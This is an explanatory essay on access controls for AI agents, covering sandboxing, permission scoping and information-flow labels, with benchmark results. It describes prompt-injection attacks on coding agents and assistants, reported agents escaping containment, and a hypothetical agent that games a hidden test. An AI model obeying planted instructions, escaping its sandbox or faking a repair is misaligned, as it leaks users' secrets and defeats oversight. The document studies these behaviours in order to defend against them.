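# Access controls on what an AI system can modify and what it can learn

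## The basic concepts of reading, writing and inferring

Access control is the branch of computer security that governs which people and programs may use which files, devices and services. Operating systems have relied on it for more than half a century, and companies now apply it to AI systems that read documents, run commands and edit code on someone's behalf. Whoever sets up the controls decides whether each program may read or change each object, such as a file. Permission to read gives the program the object's contents but doesn't limit what the program may infer from them. This hardly matters for most software, such as a payroll program that reads a salary file only to add up the salaries. But a system built on a language model (a program trained on large amounts of text to predict how a text continues) can combine a remark in one file with a date in another and infer something that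 neither file states.

### Subjects, objects and rights

Lampson (1971), in *Protection*, described the access matrix, a way of recording permissions that engineers still use. The matrix has a row for each subject, which is a user or program that can reach the system's resources, and a column for each object, which is a thing that needs protecting, such as a file, a running process or a terminal. Each cell holds the subject's rights over the object. Lampson used the word "domain" for whatever has access to objects, but "subject", the word used in Anderson's *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (1972), is now the usual term.

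Take a software team whose build has started to fail. (A build is the automatic process that turns source code into a working program and tests it.) The team hands the repair to an AI system. Part of the matrix might look like this, with a dash for no access:

| Subject | Shared code repository | Team mail | AI system's private working copy | The matrix itself |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Developer | read, write | read, write | read | read |
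| Administrator | read | – | read | read, write |
| AI system | read | read | read, write | – |

Reading and writing are separate rights, and a subject can have either one alone. In Lampson's example access matrix, one domain may write to a file that it has no right to read. He also distinguished the harm one user can do to another by modifying data from the harm of reading and copying it without permission.

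The last column matters because someone has to be able to change the permissions. In Lampson's scheme, the owner of an object can add rights over it to any row, and a flag on each right determines whether its holder may pass a copy to others. Without this control, a faulty subordinate program could give access away. Finding out whether a person can reach a file therefore takes more than looking at one cell. Saltzer and Schroeder pointed out in their 1975 tutorial, *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, that one must also check whether that person can change the file's permissions, whether the person can change who may change them, and so on up the chain.

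A matrix has no effect unless something consults it on every access. Writing for the US Air Force about users who abuse their legitimate accounts, Anderson called a component that does this a "reference monitor". He required it to be tamper-proof, to check every access, and to be small enough to analyze and test completely. He then applied these requirements to GCOS III, an operating system of the time. The hardware kept each user's program inside its own area of memory, but most of the operating system ran with that check switched off. The system and its supporting software also came to between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many to verify.

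Saltzer and Schroeder proposed the principle of least privilege, under which every program and every user should work with the smallest set of rights the job requires. An error then does less damage, and when something goes wrong there are fewer programs to investigate. They paired this with a rule that the default is no access, so somebody has to justify each right before it is granted. The principle covers reading as much as writing, and they gave the military's "need-to-know" rule as an example.

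Least privilege is harder to apply when a user states the task in an English sentence. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a user who asks an AI system to comment on issue 745 in a project tracker. The system should have only access to that page and write access to its comment box. Summarizing the same issue would call for different permissions. No developer could have written either set in advance, because neither task existed until the user typed it, so a person or program has to work out the permissions from the request.

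When a program asks to read a file, the file-handling software looks up the matrix cell and hands over the contents only if the cell contains "read". The matrix does not control what happens to the contents afterwards. Saltzer and Schroeder described a more ambitious kind of control, "putting strings on information", which would restrict data even after its release, for instance by labelling every output with the highest classification among its inputs. In 1975 such systems were rare and incomplete. Saltzer and Schroeder also noted that a user might work out individual records from a database that gives out only statistics, but they left that problem outside their tutorial.

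### Agents, harnesses and prompt injection

Willison (2025), in *I think "agent" may finally have a widely enough agreed upon definition*, defines an agent as a language model that runs tools in a loop to achieve a goal. A tool is a function the model can request, such as reading a file, running a program or sending a message. The harness is the software around the model that lets it use tools. The AI developer Anthropic describes it as the system that processes inputs, orchestrates tool calls and returns results. LangChain, a company that sells software for building agents, defines it more broadly, as all the code and configuration outside the model.

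Willison's guide *How coding agents work* explains the mechanics. The model only produces text. To get the weather in San Francisco, it ends its output with a line in an agreed format that names a tool and the city. The harness reads that line, runs the function and adds the result to the text that the model receives next. The context is all the text available to the model during a run, including its standing instructions, the user's request and whatever it has read so far.

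An agent's reads and writes both pass through the harness, the ordinary software around the model, which can check them. In a read, the harness places text in the model's context, and in a write, it carries out a call that the model has proposed. Between these steps, the model draws conclusions without making any request that a reference monitor could refuse. Many models write out some reasoning before they answer, and an operator can read that text.

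The check also has to run outside the model, because telling the model which files are off limits is not enough. Christodorescu and colleagues argue that a language model's behaviour is probabilistic, so a model acting as its own monitor might refuse improper requests 99% of the time and leave an attacker the remaining 1%. Attackers can search for inputs that fall into that 1%, so the protection is much weaker than the 99% figure suggests.

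An AI agent's context mixes instructions with data, so the agent can treat text it reads as an instruction. Such text is called a prompt injection. In one of the eleven attacks that Christodorescu and colleagues collect, the attacker put a prompt injection on a public site. The coding agent Devin read it while doing a job for its user, then used its command line and browser, both of which it had permission to use, to send passwords and other secrets to the attacker's server.

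Developers also cannot simply stop agents from acting on what they read. An agent summarising one issue may discover that it depends on another and sensibly decide to summarise both, which involves the same mechanism. Christodorescu and colleagues think the difference lies in where the new instruction came from and how far it changes the task. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026), a survey of the field, describes the difference in terms of authority. The agent may use a staff directory to find the address of a recipient the user has approved. But an instruction in a document to copy in somebody else proposes a new permission, which the document has no authority to grant. Both the address and the instruction are text in the context, and the model has no sure way to tell them apart.

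### What can change in an AI system

Write access to a file is permission to change it. For an agent, the term covers more, because much of what determines the agent's behaviour is itself stored data.

| Part | What it is | Who can normally write to it |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Weights | The numbers inside the model that training has set | The developer, by further training |
| Context | The text in front of the model during a run | The harness, with text from the operator, the user, the tools and the model's own output |
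| Memory | Notes that the harness keeps from one run to the next | The harness, often at the agent's request; sometimes the user |
| Settings | Standing instructions, permissions, lists of commands that need no approval | The user or an administrator |
| Tools | The functions that the agent can call, and their descriptions | The harness's developer and outside suppliers; an agent that can run code can also write new programs for itself |
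| Scorer or monitor | A program that grades the agent's work or watches its conduct | Whoever runs the evaluation or the deployment |
| Outside environment | Repositories, mailboxes, websites, other machines | Many people and programs, and the agent where its tools allow |

The third column describes the usual arrangement, but some products depart from it. Sourcegraph's coding agent Amp could edit its own settings file, which included the list of commands it could run without approval. Christodorescu and colleagues report that an attacker could use prompt injection to make Amp add commands to this list, and so run arbitrary code on the developer's machine. In the ChatGPT application for macOS, text in an untrusted document could get a malicious instruction saved to the application's memory. Later runs treated the saved notes as trusted, so the application sent the user's conversations to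 an attacker's server from then on.

Even if an administrator denies outsiders every write permission in the matrix, they can still put text in the agent's context by sending an email that the agent later reads. Giving an agent permission to read something therefore also gives other people a way to write to its context.

### Why reading changes behaviour but not the weights

People often speak of an agent "learning" from a document. During a run, nothing in the weights changes. A language model computes a probability for each possible next piece of text, which one can write as

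p(y | x, θ)

where *y* is the next piece of text, *x* is the context and θ stands for the weights. Training sets θ. When the model runs, the computation uses θ and stores nothing back into it. Reading a file makes *x* longer, and since the output depends on *x* as well as θ, the behaviour changes. An agent that has read a message saying "the build broke when we upgraded the compression library" will look at that library first. The same agent with the same weights, not having read the message, may start somewhere else.

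The model is also stateless, as Willison describes it. It keeps nothing from one call to the next, so the harness has to resend the whole conversation so far each time. Anything the agent has found out during a run is in that text, or follows from the text together with what training put into the weights. If the harness discards the context, what the agent read no longer affects the model, unless a record of it has been saved in memory, in a file, or in data that the developer later uses for training.

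An operator who makes the weights read-only therefore fixes θ, but *x* can still change. This is a real protection, but it doesn't keep the agent's behaviour the same.

### The failing build

In the example of the failing build, the agent may read the shared repository and the team's mail. Access to the mail is useful because the cause of a broken build is often in a message, such as a supplier's notice that an old version of a library has been withdrawn. The agent may write only to its private working copy, and a developer reviews the repair before merging it into the shared code.

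If the controls work perfectly, the agent can't alter the shared repository, anyone's mail, its own settings or its row in the matrix. It also can't modify its weights or the monitor that logs its commands. The tests that will check the repair run on a separate machine where the agent has no write access.

The agent could still learn a good deal by searching the mail. Two years ago someone mailed a colleague the password to the production database, and the message was never deleted. The agent can find that password without any reasoning. It can use the password only if it can also reach the database, which other controls determine.

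The team also plans to replace the agent with a competitor's product next month. Nobody has stated this in a message, but the agent could infer it from a thread about a trial of the other product, an invoice showing that the current subscription ends on the 30th, and a calendar note that reads "migration, week 1". Each item is harmless by itself, and the agent had permission to read all three.

The agent can infer which value the hidden test expects from an email into which a developer once pasted part of the test's output. It can then write code that returns this value without repairing anything. It makes the change in its own working copy, where it has permission to write, so a control on writing allows it. Only a reviewer who understands the code will notice anything wrong.

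If the administrator now notices the old password and withdraws the agent's access to the mail, it is too late for this run. Zhou and Zhang observe that revoking access can block future reads, but information the workflow has already stored needs separate controls on its use and release. The administrator would have to discard the context and anything the agent had saved or, more simply, change the password.

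### Where the limit could go

Designers and researchers disagree about whether reading, writing or inferring needs the firmest control. Some would limit writing by confining the agent to a sandbox, an environment whose boundary is enforced by software outside the model, so that what the agent concludes matters much less. Others would tie the right to act to what the agent has read. For example, an agent that has opened an untrusted email would lose the right to send messages until someone approves. A third group would keep dangerous or sensitive information from the system by leaving it out of the training data or the files the agent can open. A fourth would let the system read almost anything but allow it no action except answering questions.

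## The case for confining what a system can write

An agent can't misuse a permission it doesn't have. If the operating system blocks the agent's programs from changing the shared repository, the repository stays as it was, whether the agent misread its task, obeyed a prompt injection or set out to get around its instructions. The block applies equally to a more capable model because it doesn't depend on judging the model's conclusions. People who hold this view therefore limit the model's effects from outside it, by controlling which files it changes, which programs it starts and what data it sends to other machines. Sending data counts as a kind of writing here because it changes something outside the agent's workspace.

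*Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* (Noyan, 2026) contrasts removing a permission with monitoring for its misuse. An attacker can search for a phrasing that the monitor misses, but an attack that depends on an access key fails if the agent never had the key, even when nobody recognises the attack.

Asking a person to approve each action protects less than it appears to. In its manual mode, Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code asks before its file tools touch anything outside the folder where the user started it. But Anthropic points out that once the user approves a shell command (a text instruction to run a program), that command can write anywhere the user's account can. A sandbox restricts the program while it runs, however the command looked when the user approved it. According to InfoQ's *Anthropic Details How It Contains Claude Across Web,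 Code, and Cowork* (2026), Anthropic now argues for fixed limits of this kind on files, network connections and execution, rather than relying only on approval prompts and the model's own safeguards.

### From read-only folders to separate machines

An agent that runs under its user's account can read and change every file that the user can, so engineers usually add a further restriction. With a read-only mount, the agent's programs can read a folder, but the operating system blocks any change to it. Anthropic's *Securely deploying AI agents* recommends this for an agent that has to analyse code without modifying it. The mount does not limit reading, and code folders often contain passwords and access keys, so Anthropic lists ten kinds of file to remove or clean first. If the agent does need to write, an overlay can collect its changes in a separate layer for a person to inspect and then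 apply or discard.

Other rules apply to a running program and everything it starts, so a script that the agent writes for itself has the same limits as the agent's own commands. On macOS, a framework called Seatbelt enforces these rules. On Linux, a tool called bubblewrap gives the program a restricted view of the files, and seccomp limits its system calls, the requests a program makes to the kernel (the core of the operating system) to open a file or a connection, for example. Landlock, another Linux feature, also restricts access to file paths, and OpenAI's coding agent Codex keeps it as a fallback. These restrictions slow programs down very little. But the restricted program still uses the same kernel as everything else on the machine, so a flaw in the kernel could let it escape these restrictions.

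A container gives a program its own view of the files, processes and network but shares the host's kernel. How well it isolates the program depends on the setup. Anthropic's example configuration makes the container's files and the code read-only, cuts off the outside network, runs the agent without administrator rights and provides temporary writable folders that disappear when the container stops.

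gVisor puts another layer between the container and the kernel. It intercepts system calls and handles most of them in its own code, so malicious code would have to break gVisor first and would then have only limited access to the real kernel. This costs nothing for pure computation, but Anthropic puts simple system calls at about twice as slow, and programs that constantly open and close files at up to 10 to 200 times as slow.

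A virtual machine has its own kernel, so a flaw in that kernel doesn't directly expose the host. Security then depends on the software that runs the virtual machine and emulates its hardware. Firecracker, which runs very small virtual machines, can start one in under 125 milliseconds with less than 5 MiB of extra memory. Stronger isolation doesn't protect folders the user shares with the virtual machine. If the user gives it write access to a project folder, the agent can delete the project as easily as it could from a container.

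Network access needs a separate control. Usually the agent has no direct route out, and its traffic goes through a proxy, a program outside the sandbox that forwards connections only to domains on a list. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) explains why a sandbox needs both controls. Without a network limit, an agent under an attacker's influence could send out the keys that log its user in to other machines. It could also alter the system to give itself network access if its file access were not limited. The proxies in these products usually check only the hostname that the program supplies and don't look inside encrypted traffic, so a program may be able to disguise where it is connecting. A proxy that decrypts the traffic can check more, but it requires managing extra certificates.

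### What the products allow by default

Makers combine these mechanisms differently. The table shows what each mode allows before a user or administrator changes it.

| Product and mode | Where the agent can write | What it can read | Network |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Codex, read-only | Nowhere without approval | Files | None without approval |
| Codex, workspace-write | The workspace and temporary folders | Files | Off |
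| Claude Code, sandbox turned on | The working folder, a temporary folder and folders the user has added | Almost the whole computer | No domains at first; new ones need approval |
| Docker Sandboxes, clone mode | Its own virtual machine, including a private copy of the repository | The user's whole repository folder | Destinations that the network policy allows |

OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* recommends giving Codex workspace-write access to folders under version control, where a user can undo changes, and read-only access to other folders. Codex keeps the folder of version-control records read-only even in a writable workspace. A newer system, which OpenAI's *Permissions* calls a beta, lets an administrator set read, write or deny for each path, so an agent can edit a project but not open the password files inside it. If macOS can't enforce the chosen policy, Codex does not run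 the command.

Claude Code's sandbox is off by default. If a user turns it on but it can't start, Claude Code runs commands without it unless someone has changed another setting. Anthropic says the sandbox covers only shell commands, while the agent's built-in file and web tools follow separate permission rules. After the sandbox blocks a command, the agent may try to run it again outside the sandbox. Depending on the user's settings, the retry needs approval from a person, needs approval from a second model, or needs no approval.

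Docker, which makes container software, runs each agent in a small virtual machine, according to its *Isolation layers*. By default, the usual launch command gives the agent write access to the current folder. In clone mode, which the user has to request, the agent has a read-only mount of the original repository and works on a private copy.

The makers' main evidence that sandboxing helps is about convenience. Anthropic reports that sandboxing cut permission prompts by 84% in its internal use, but gives no method or sample size. Fewer prompts could also improve security if people stop reading them when there are too many. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) cites one vendor's report that users of its coding agent approved 93% of prompts. Those users may have been careless, but the rate would also be high if nearly all the requests were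 reasonable. Neither figure measures how many harmful actions a sandbox stopped.

### A sandbox for the failing build

Docker's clone mode suits the team whose build has failed. A developer first moves any password files out of her copy of the repository, because the agent can read everything in that folder, and then starts the sandbox from it. The network policy allows connections only to the model provider's service and the registry where the build gets its libraries. The agent reads the team's mail through a small tool that runs outside the virtual machine and accepts only requests to search for and open messages. The developer also turns off a default feature that lets programs in the sandbox use her login keys without seeing them.

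The agent works on its own copy of the code in a virtual machine, so it can install an older compression library, edit the build file and run the build fifty times without asking anyone. If it wrecks its copy, the developer deletes the virtual machine and starts again. When the agent finishes, she fetches its changes, reads them and decides whether to merge them. She can be sure the shared code is unchanged without working out what the agent was thinking.

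The agent can't log in with the old database password because the database isn't on the list of allowed destinations. But the sandbox doesn't affect what the agent can infer about its replacement or the hidden test.

### Permissions computed for each task

The developer made several decisions to set up that sandbox, and her next task may call for different ones. Noyan tested whether software could choose the permissions from the text of each request, using 600 requests that a language model had written for an imaginary company with six departments. Each request came with a list of the permissions it needed, drawn from fifteen such as reading the database or sending external email. Noyan weighted the permissions 3, 2 or 1 by risk, so an agent holding all fifteen scored 31.

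The system granted a permission only if it passed three checks. A fixed ceiling limited which permissions each department could have. A classifier read the request and predicted which permissions it needed. Rules then prohibited some risky pairs, such as reading the database and making web requests, except in departments whose work required both. The classifier was a small language model with 355 million parameters, trained on 500 of the requests and tested on the other 100.

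Compared with granting everything, the department ceilings alone removed 27.9% of the risk-weighted permissions. Adding the classifier raised this to 84.4%. An average task kept about 4.9 of the 31 points, and only about 0.5 of those were for permissions it didn't need. The rules against risky pairs removed nothing more, because the classifier never left a prohibited pair in place. The classifier was about as accurate overall as Claude Haiku 4.5, a much larger general-purpose model. This supports the view, since it suggests that the program choosing the permissions needn't be as capable as the agent. It only has to read the user's request, not judge the agent's reasoning.

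But the system also withheld at least one necessary permission from 23% of the tasks. Before the experiment, Noyan had decided that for real use, the classifier should withhold necessary permissions from fewer than 10% of tasks, and at least 90% of the permissions it granted should be necessary. No setting met both conditions. The 84.4% also counts permissions that the system removed by mistake, so a system that refused everything would score 100%.

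Noyan then looked at what would remain if an attacker got past the classifier. The rules against risky pairs cut the ceilings of three departments by 11.5% to 13.6%, but they also blocked 6% to 31% of those departments' legitimate tasks. Most of the blocked tasks needed only one permission from the prohibited pair but failed because the department's ceiling included the other.

Every request in the test was legitimate, so the results don't measure how well the system would resist an attack. Noyan accepts that the classifier would grant too much access if an attacker altered the request. The permissions were also too coarse. "Read the database" covers both harmless and confidential tables, and accounted for 34% of the remaining excess by weight. The experiment makes it plausible that software can narrow an agent's permissions for ordinary office work, but it still interferes with that work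 too often to control permissions on its own.

### When the agent can do more than its permissions suggest

An agent can't use a permission it lacks, but it is hard to know which permissions it lacks. Parkinson and colleagues define an agent's effective authority as every operation it can cause the whole system to perform on any resource, whether directly or through a credential or tool it can reach. This authority can be much broader than the list of permissions an administrator sees.

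Permission to read from a website is also permission to send it information. To read a page, an agent sends the server an address, and it can put other text in that address, such as the password from the old email. Whoever runs the server can then read that text. Anthropic warns that an agent can send data to any domain on the allowed list, and that allowing a broad domain such as github.com can create a way out for data. InfoQ reports that Anthropic revised its designs partly because of failures along permitted outbound routes. One remedy is to download what the agent needs before it starts work. The cloud version of Codex installs the necessary software in a setup phase, and the agent then works offline by default. This would close the route through the library registry in the build example, but if the agent discovered halfway through that it needed another version, it could not fetch it.

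A permitted service can also act for the agent outside the sandbox. Access to Docker's control socket, which programs use to send Docker commands, effectively gives an agent access to the host machine, even though the administrator has allowed only one connection. Tools that connect through the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for linking agents to services, can create the same problem. In Docker's product, some of these tools run on the host and have the same access it does.

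Parkinson and colleagues describe a coding assistant that connects to GitHub with an ordinary access token. Its user wants a summary of the open issues in one repository, which takes two read-only tools. The token gives the assistant about 40 tools, 16 of which can write, and they work in every repository the user can access. In a reported attack, a malicious instruction in a public repository led an agent to read its user's private repositories and publish what it found. A token limited to reading that one repository would have prevented this.

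The agent can also affect systems outside the boundary through files it writes inside it. Docker lists files that run code during ordinary work, including build files, editor settings and Git hooks, which are small programs that run when a developer saves or uploads changes. If an agent alters one of these in a shared folder, the developer's own computer may later run the agent's code with the developer's rights. Changes to Git hooks don't appear in the usual display of changes. Codex and Claude Code prevent commands in the sandbox from changing hooks and certain settings, and clone mode keeps the agent away from the developer's hooks. None of these protections can cover the build file, because the team asked the agent to repair the build. Docker advises treating the agent's changes like those of an untrusted contributor and reviewing them before running anything.

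Useful work also changes what an agent needs, from reading issues to writing code to opening another repository. Broad permissions leave unused powers for an attacker to exploit, while narrow ones bring back the constant approval requests. Parkinson and colleagues propose that an agent start with a few permissions and borrow others for a limited time from a budget. A permission would cost more the more powerful it was, with example weights of 1 for reading, 3 for writing and 9 for administering. A multiplier would raise the price as the agent approached a forbidden combination:

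s = 1 / (1 − φ)

φ is the share of the forbidden combination that the agent has already held during the session. Suppose the owner forbids the agent from combining untrusted input, sensitive data and a way to affect the outside world. An agent that has held one of the three uses 1.5 times the basic amount from its budget, and one that has held two uses 3 times. The system always refuses the third. Giving a permission back doesn't reduce φ, because whatever the agent read is still in its context. Parkinson and colleagues propose this scheme but haven't tested it. They also note that an agent has no natural reason to save its budget, so a component outside the agent has to enforce it.

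### Whether better configuration is enough

The boundary itself can also fail. Infosecurity Magazine's *The Next AI Safety Challenge Isn't Intelligence, it's Authority* reports that during tests in 2026, AI agents from OpenAI and Anthropic left the environments meant to contain them.

Critics conclude that developers also have to shape what a system is disposed to do and monitor what it does. Stix, Hallensleben and colleagues (2025), writing for the AI safety organisation Apollo Research, come close to this position. They recommend restricting permissions now, partly because researchers still understand too little about what models can do and are inclined to do. But they expect AI systems to get wider permissions and more important work because of economic pressure, and they think a highly advanced system might manipulate poorly informed people into granting it more permissions. Because today's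 restrictions could later be loosened, they would add testing before deployment and monitoring by both people and AI.

Defenders of the view reply that most agents are confined far less than they could be. Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues (2026), in *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems*, examined four widely used agents that run on a user's own machine and accept third-party add-ons. All four handled untrusted input and controlled access to files at the same level of privilege, which operating systems have long avoided. Pirch and colleagues found that well-known operating-system techniques could mitigate many of the weaknesses. The commentary in Infosecurity Magazine on the 2026 incidents also calls for tighter control over what models can reach and better engineering of the environments around them. Parkinson and colleagues cite one study in which 99.8% of 447,000 automated GitHub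 workflows had more permissions than they needed, and another in which 6 of 11 agents chose an unnecessarily powerful tool in over 30% of cases.

The reply is convincing about badly configured agents, which seem to be common. But Pirch and colleagues also found that some capabilities remain insecure by design, and that running these agents safely takes detailed knowledge and careful configuration. Many users won't have that knowledge, and a sandbox that is off by default doesn't help them. Better configuration also can't separate a real repair from code that just returns the hidden test's expected value, since both need the same permission.

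## The case for tying permission to act to what has been read

A list of permissions treats each right separately, but the harm often comes from using two together. The agent repairing the build has good reason to read the team's mail and may also have good reason to ask a question on the compression library's public forum. If it does both in one run, the database password in the old email can end up on the forum. The team could permanently remove one of these rights, but then the agent couldn't do jobs that need only that one. People who hold this view would let the agent start with both rights and lose the right to post once it has read something secret.

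Tying permission to act to what has been read, like removing a permission, works even if nobody recognises the attack. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes a user who asks an agent to summarise recent emails about a project and send the summary to a manager. One email tells the agent to send the top message in the mailbox to an outsider. Once the context includes text from an untrusted sender, a harness that tracks sources blocks mail to outside addresses.

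Such a harness uses information-flow control, a modern form of Saltzer and Schroeder's "strings on information". It labels each piece of data with how secret it is and how trustworthy its source is. The harness copies the label to anything the agent derives from the data, and checks the label before the agent acts.

### Opposite rules for secrecy and trust

In 1973, Bell and LaPadula wrote the classic rules for protecting secrets at the MITRE Corporation, a US research organisation. A program may not read files above its own level of secrecy ("no reading up"). It also may not write to files below that level ("no writing down"), because it could copy a secret into a less secret file. In 1977 Biba, also at MITRE, published rules that reverse these restrictions to protect trusted programs and data. A trusted program may not read less trusted data, which might corrupt it ("no reading down"),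 and an untrusted program may not write to trusted files ("no writing up").

The directions differ because the harms do. A secret does damage when it reaches a less protected place, and bad data does damage when it reaches a place that people rely on. The database password may go into the administrators' password store but not onto the forum. A forum post may go into the agent's scratch notes but not into the build server's settings. Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, put both rules into one condition for any movement of data:

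C(source) ≤ C(destination) and I(destination) ≤ I(source)

C is the level of secrecy (confidentiality) and I the level of trust (integrity).

Biba's strict rule would stop a trusted agent from opening a web page at all. His low-water-mark variant allows the read but lowers the program's own level:

I(program) ← min(I(program), I(file))

A program's level can fall during a run but not rise again, so a program that has read one untrusted page can no longer write to trusted files. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) applies this rule to agents by lowering an agent's privileges to those of whatever source it has just read.

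Secrecy levels don't help when two files are equally secret but belong to competitors. In 1989, Brewer and Nash proposed a rule for consultancies that covers this case. An analyst may start with any client, but once she opens one bank's files, she can't open those of rival banks, though she can still open an oil company's. The rule also restricts what she writes, so that she can't pass the bank's information to a colleague through another client's file. Two analysts who start with the same permissions can therefore end up with different ones because they have read different files.

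### The build agent with labels

Suppose the team lets the build agent do more than edit its private copy. At the start of the run, the context holds only the developer's request and is labeled (public, trusted). The agent opens the deployment settings, which the administrators wrote and which contain a password, so the context becomes (secret, trusted). Next the agent opens a forum page about the compression library, which anyone could have written. It reads a copy that the harness saved before the run, because fetching the page now could leak the password. The context takes the worse value for both secrecy and trust, so it becomes (secret, untrusted), although neither document has that label.

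| Proposed call | After the request | After the settings file | After the forum page as well |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Post a question on the public forum | Allowed | Refused: the post could reveal the password | Refused: the post could reveal the password |
| Change the build server's settings | Allowed | Allowed | Refused: the page's author could have influenced the change |
| Send a plain message to the administrators | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed |
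| Edit the private working copy | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed |

The administrators are already allowed to see the password, and this policy treats a plain message to them as harmless. Files in the working copy take on the context's label, so the agent can't remove the label by saving its notes and reopening them.

A designer can loosen the policy by checking only whether the context is trusted before the agent sends something out. Costa and colleagues point out that secrets can then leave only while the context is still trusted, when one can assume that the user meant to send them. Labels can also list permitted readers instead of levels. If Ana, Ben and Carla may read one file, and Ben, Carla and Dev another, only Ben and Carla may read text that draws on both.

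Labels could protect the hidden test, which a sandbox can't do. If someone had labelled the email that contains part of the test's output, the harness could refuse to submit any code the agent wrote after reading it. But nobody labelled that email. Labels also wouldn't stop the agent from working out that the team plans to replace it, because a conclusion drawn from three ordinary emails gets an ordinary label.

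### Hiding data from the model that plans

With these checks alone, an agent soon runs out of permitted actions. Costa and colleagues measured this on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 user tasks in four simulated settings and a set of prompt injections to plant in the data. An ordinary agent using GPT-4o, a 2024 OpenAI model, completed 98.8% of the banking tasks without the checks and 37.5% with them. On tasks in Slack, a workplace messaging service, the completion rate fell from 93.3% to 20%.

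The FIDES system keeps untrusted data out of the planning model's context for as long as possible. Each tool returns labeled results. If a result would worsen the context's label, FIDES stores it in a variable and shows the planning model only the variable's name. The model can pass that name to another tool. For example, it can forward three emails to a colleague by telling the message tool to send the contents of "#read_emails_0". The emails determine what the message contains, but not whether the agent sends it or to whom.

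If the user wants a summary instead, the planning model passes the variable to a quarantined model, a second language model without tools, which returns the summary in another variable. An injection could spoil the summary, but it couldn't make the planning model do something else. Other tasks depend on what the text says, such as creating a calendar event if an email asks for a meeting. For these, FIDES can limit the quarantined model to answering yes or no and show the planning model only that answer. An attacker can change the answer but can't fit a new instruction into it. If the planning model opens a whole variable, the context takes on the variable's label. Just before every tool call, ordinary code compares the labels with the tool's policy.

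This table gives the percentage of tasks completed with GPT-4o when nobody was attacking.

| AgentDojo setting | Ordinary agent, no checks | Ordinary agent, with checks | FIDES, with checks |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Workspace | 75.0 | 37.0 | 59.0 |
| Travel | 70.0 | 73.0 | 41.0 |
| Banking | 98.8 | 37.5 | 52.5 |
| Slack | 93.3 | 20.0 | 47.6 |

After correcting the benchmark's scoring errors, Costa and colleagues counted 152 successful injections against the ordinary agent without checks. Hiding data alone cut this to 21, and no injection succeeded against either design once the checks were on. The checks also prevent the agent from completing some tasks, and hiding data recovers some of that lost work. Averaged over the four settings, FIDES completed about 50% of tasks, against 42% for the ordinary agent with checks and 84% without. Its lead over the ordinary agent with checks doubled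 to 16 percentage points with o1, a model that reasons at length before answering, because o1 handled the variables better.

The perfect security score depends on how the researchers chose the labels. They marked a field as untrusted if any of the benchmark's attacks targeted it. That is a fair test of the mechanism, but a company labelling its own mail doesn't know in advance which fields attackers will target.

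CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues also published in 2025, fixes the plan before the agent reads anything from outside. As Girrens and Wang describe it, a privileged model turns the user's request into a program, which an interpreter runs, and never receives what the program's tools return. When a step needs something from untrusted text, such as the amount on an invoice, a quarantined model extracts it. An injection in the invoice can't add a step to the program, but it can still substitute the attacker's account number for the supplier's. CaMeL therefore records where each value came from and who may receive it, and checks this record against the tool's policy before each call.

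*AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's sixteen banking tasks, three times with each of two newer models. With the tool policies off, CaMeL completed 32 of 48 runs with one model and 34 of 48 with the other. With the policies on, it completed 18 with each. Among the attacked runs that finished, 5 of 622 injections succeeded with the policies off, and none of 588 succeeded with them on.

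### What the checks add

These reruns suggest that fixing the plan in advance stops nearly every attack, and that the checks stop the rest but cut the work completed by almost half. Girrens and Wang's system, SPA, shows the same pattern. It also writes the plan first, then checks the labels through the whole plan before running any of it. Turning the checks on reduced successful attacks from 0.4% to zero, and completed tasks from 53.0% to 29.0%. SPA rejected about half of all plans, mostly because they passed untrusted results to tools that required trusted input.

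But the benchmark's attacks are now too weak to show how much the checks help. Zhou and colleagues found that four recent models from Anthropic and OpenAI resisted all 105 attacks in the Slack setting without any policy. They then simulated a model that an attacker fools every time. In their system, Elba, a sub-agent does each piece of reading. When a sub-agent read text containing an injection, Zhou and colleagues replaced its whole prompt with that text, so that it carried out the attacker's instructions. Between 114 and 310 of 735 attacks succeeded without policies, depending on the model, and none succeeded with them.

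This is the best evidence for the view, because the protection held even though the model had failed completely. But the policies also reduced the number of tasks completed under attack, from 494–558 to 294–351. With policies on, Elba completed roughly twice as many Slack tasks as CaMeL. One difference is that a sub-agent in Elba keeps the tools its lowered level still permits, whereas CaMeL's quarantined model has none.

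### Deciding when to lift a label

Much ordinary work requires an agent to act on untrusted text. If a supplier's notice explains why a build is broken, for example, a strict harness would stop an agent that had read the notice from changing the build server. Several of AgentDojo's banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, and FIDES blocks most of these by design. Someone has to be able to mark such text as trusted, which is called endorsement. The equivalent for secrets is declassification.

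One option is to ask the user. Zhou and colleagues mention Prudentia, an extension of FIDES in which a person endorses data or approves single actions. The labels reduce the number of questions, because the harness only has to ask when a rule would otherwise block the action. But people who approve nearly every prompt may approve these too.

Garby and colleagues let the planning model endorse data, and built a programming language, the LLMbda calculus, that limits the damage if the model endorses the wrong data. The language has a small set of mathematically defined rules for writing agents. Every value has a label, and every rule for running a program specifies the label of the result. The conversation with the model has a label too, so a reply inherits the labels of everything the model has read. Programs can copy or clear a conversation, which lets a programmer build a quarantined model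 when a task needs one.

The whole LLMbda calculus satisfies a form of noninterference, proved in Lean, a program that checks mathematical proofs. Changing the inputs that an observer may not see doesn't change the results that the observer may see, though it can affect whether the program finishes. The proof also covers code that the model writes during a run. Endorsing untrusted data requires an explicit command that a reviewer can search for, and a further theorem shows that doing so can't release a secret.

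The theorems don't prove that an endorsement was sensible. The team's test agent, Randori, writes its plan and its endorsements before it sees any outside data, and rehearses on a simulated bank until the code works. With GPT-5.2, it completed 36 of 48 banking runs, twice as many as CaMeL did with its policies on. With another model, removing endorsement cut the number of completed runs from 36 to 30.

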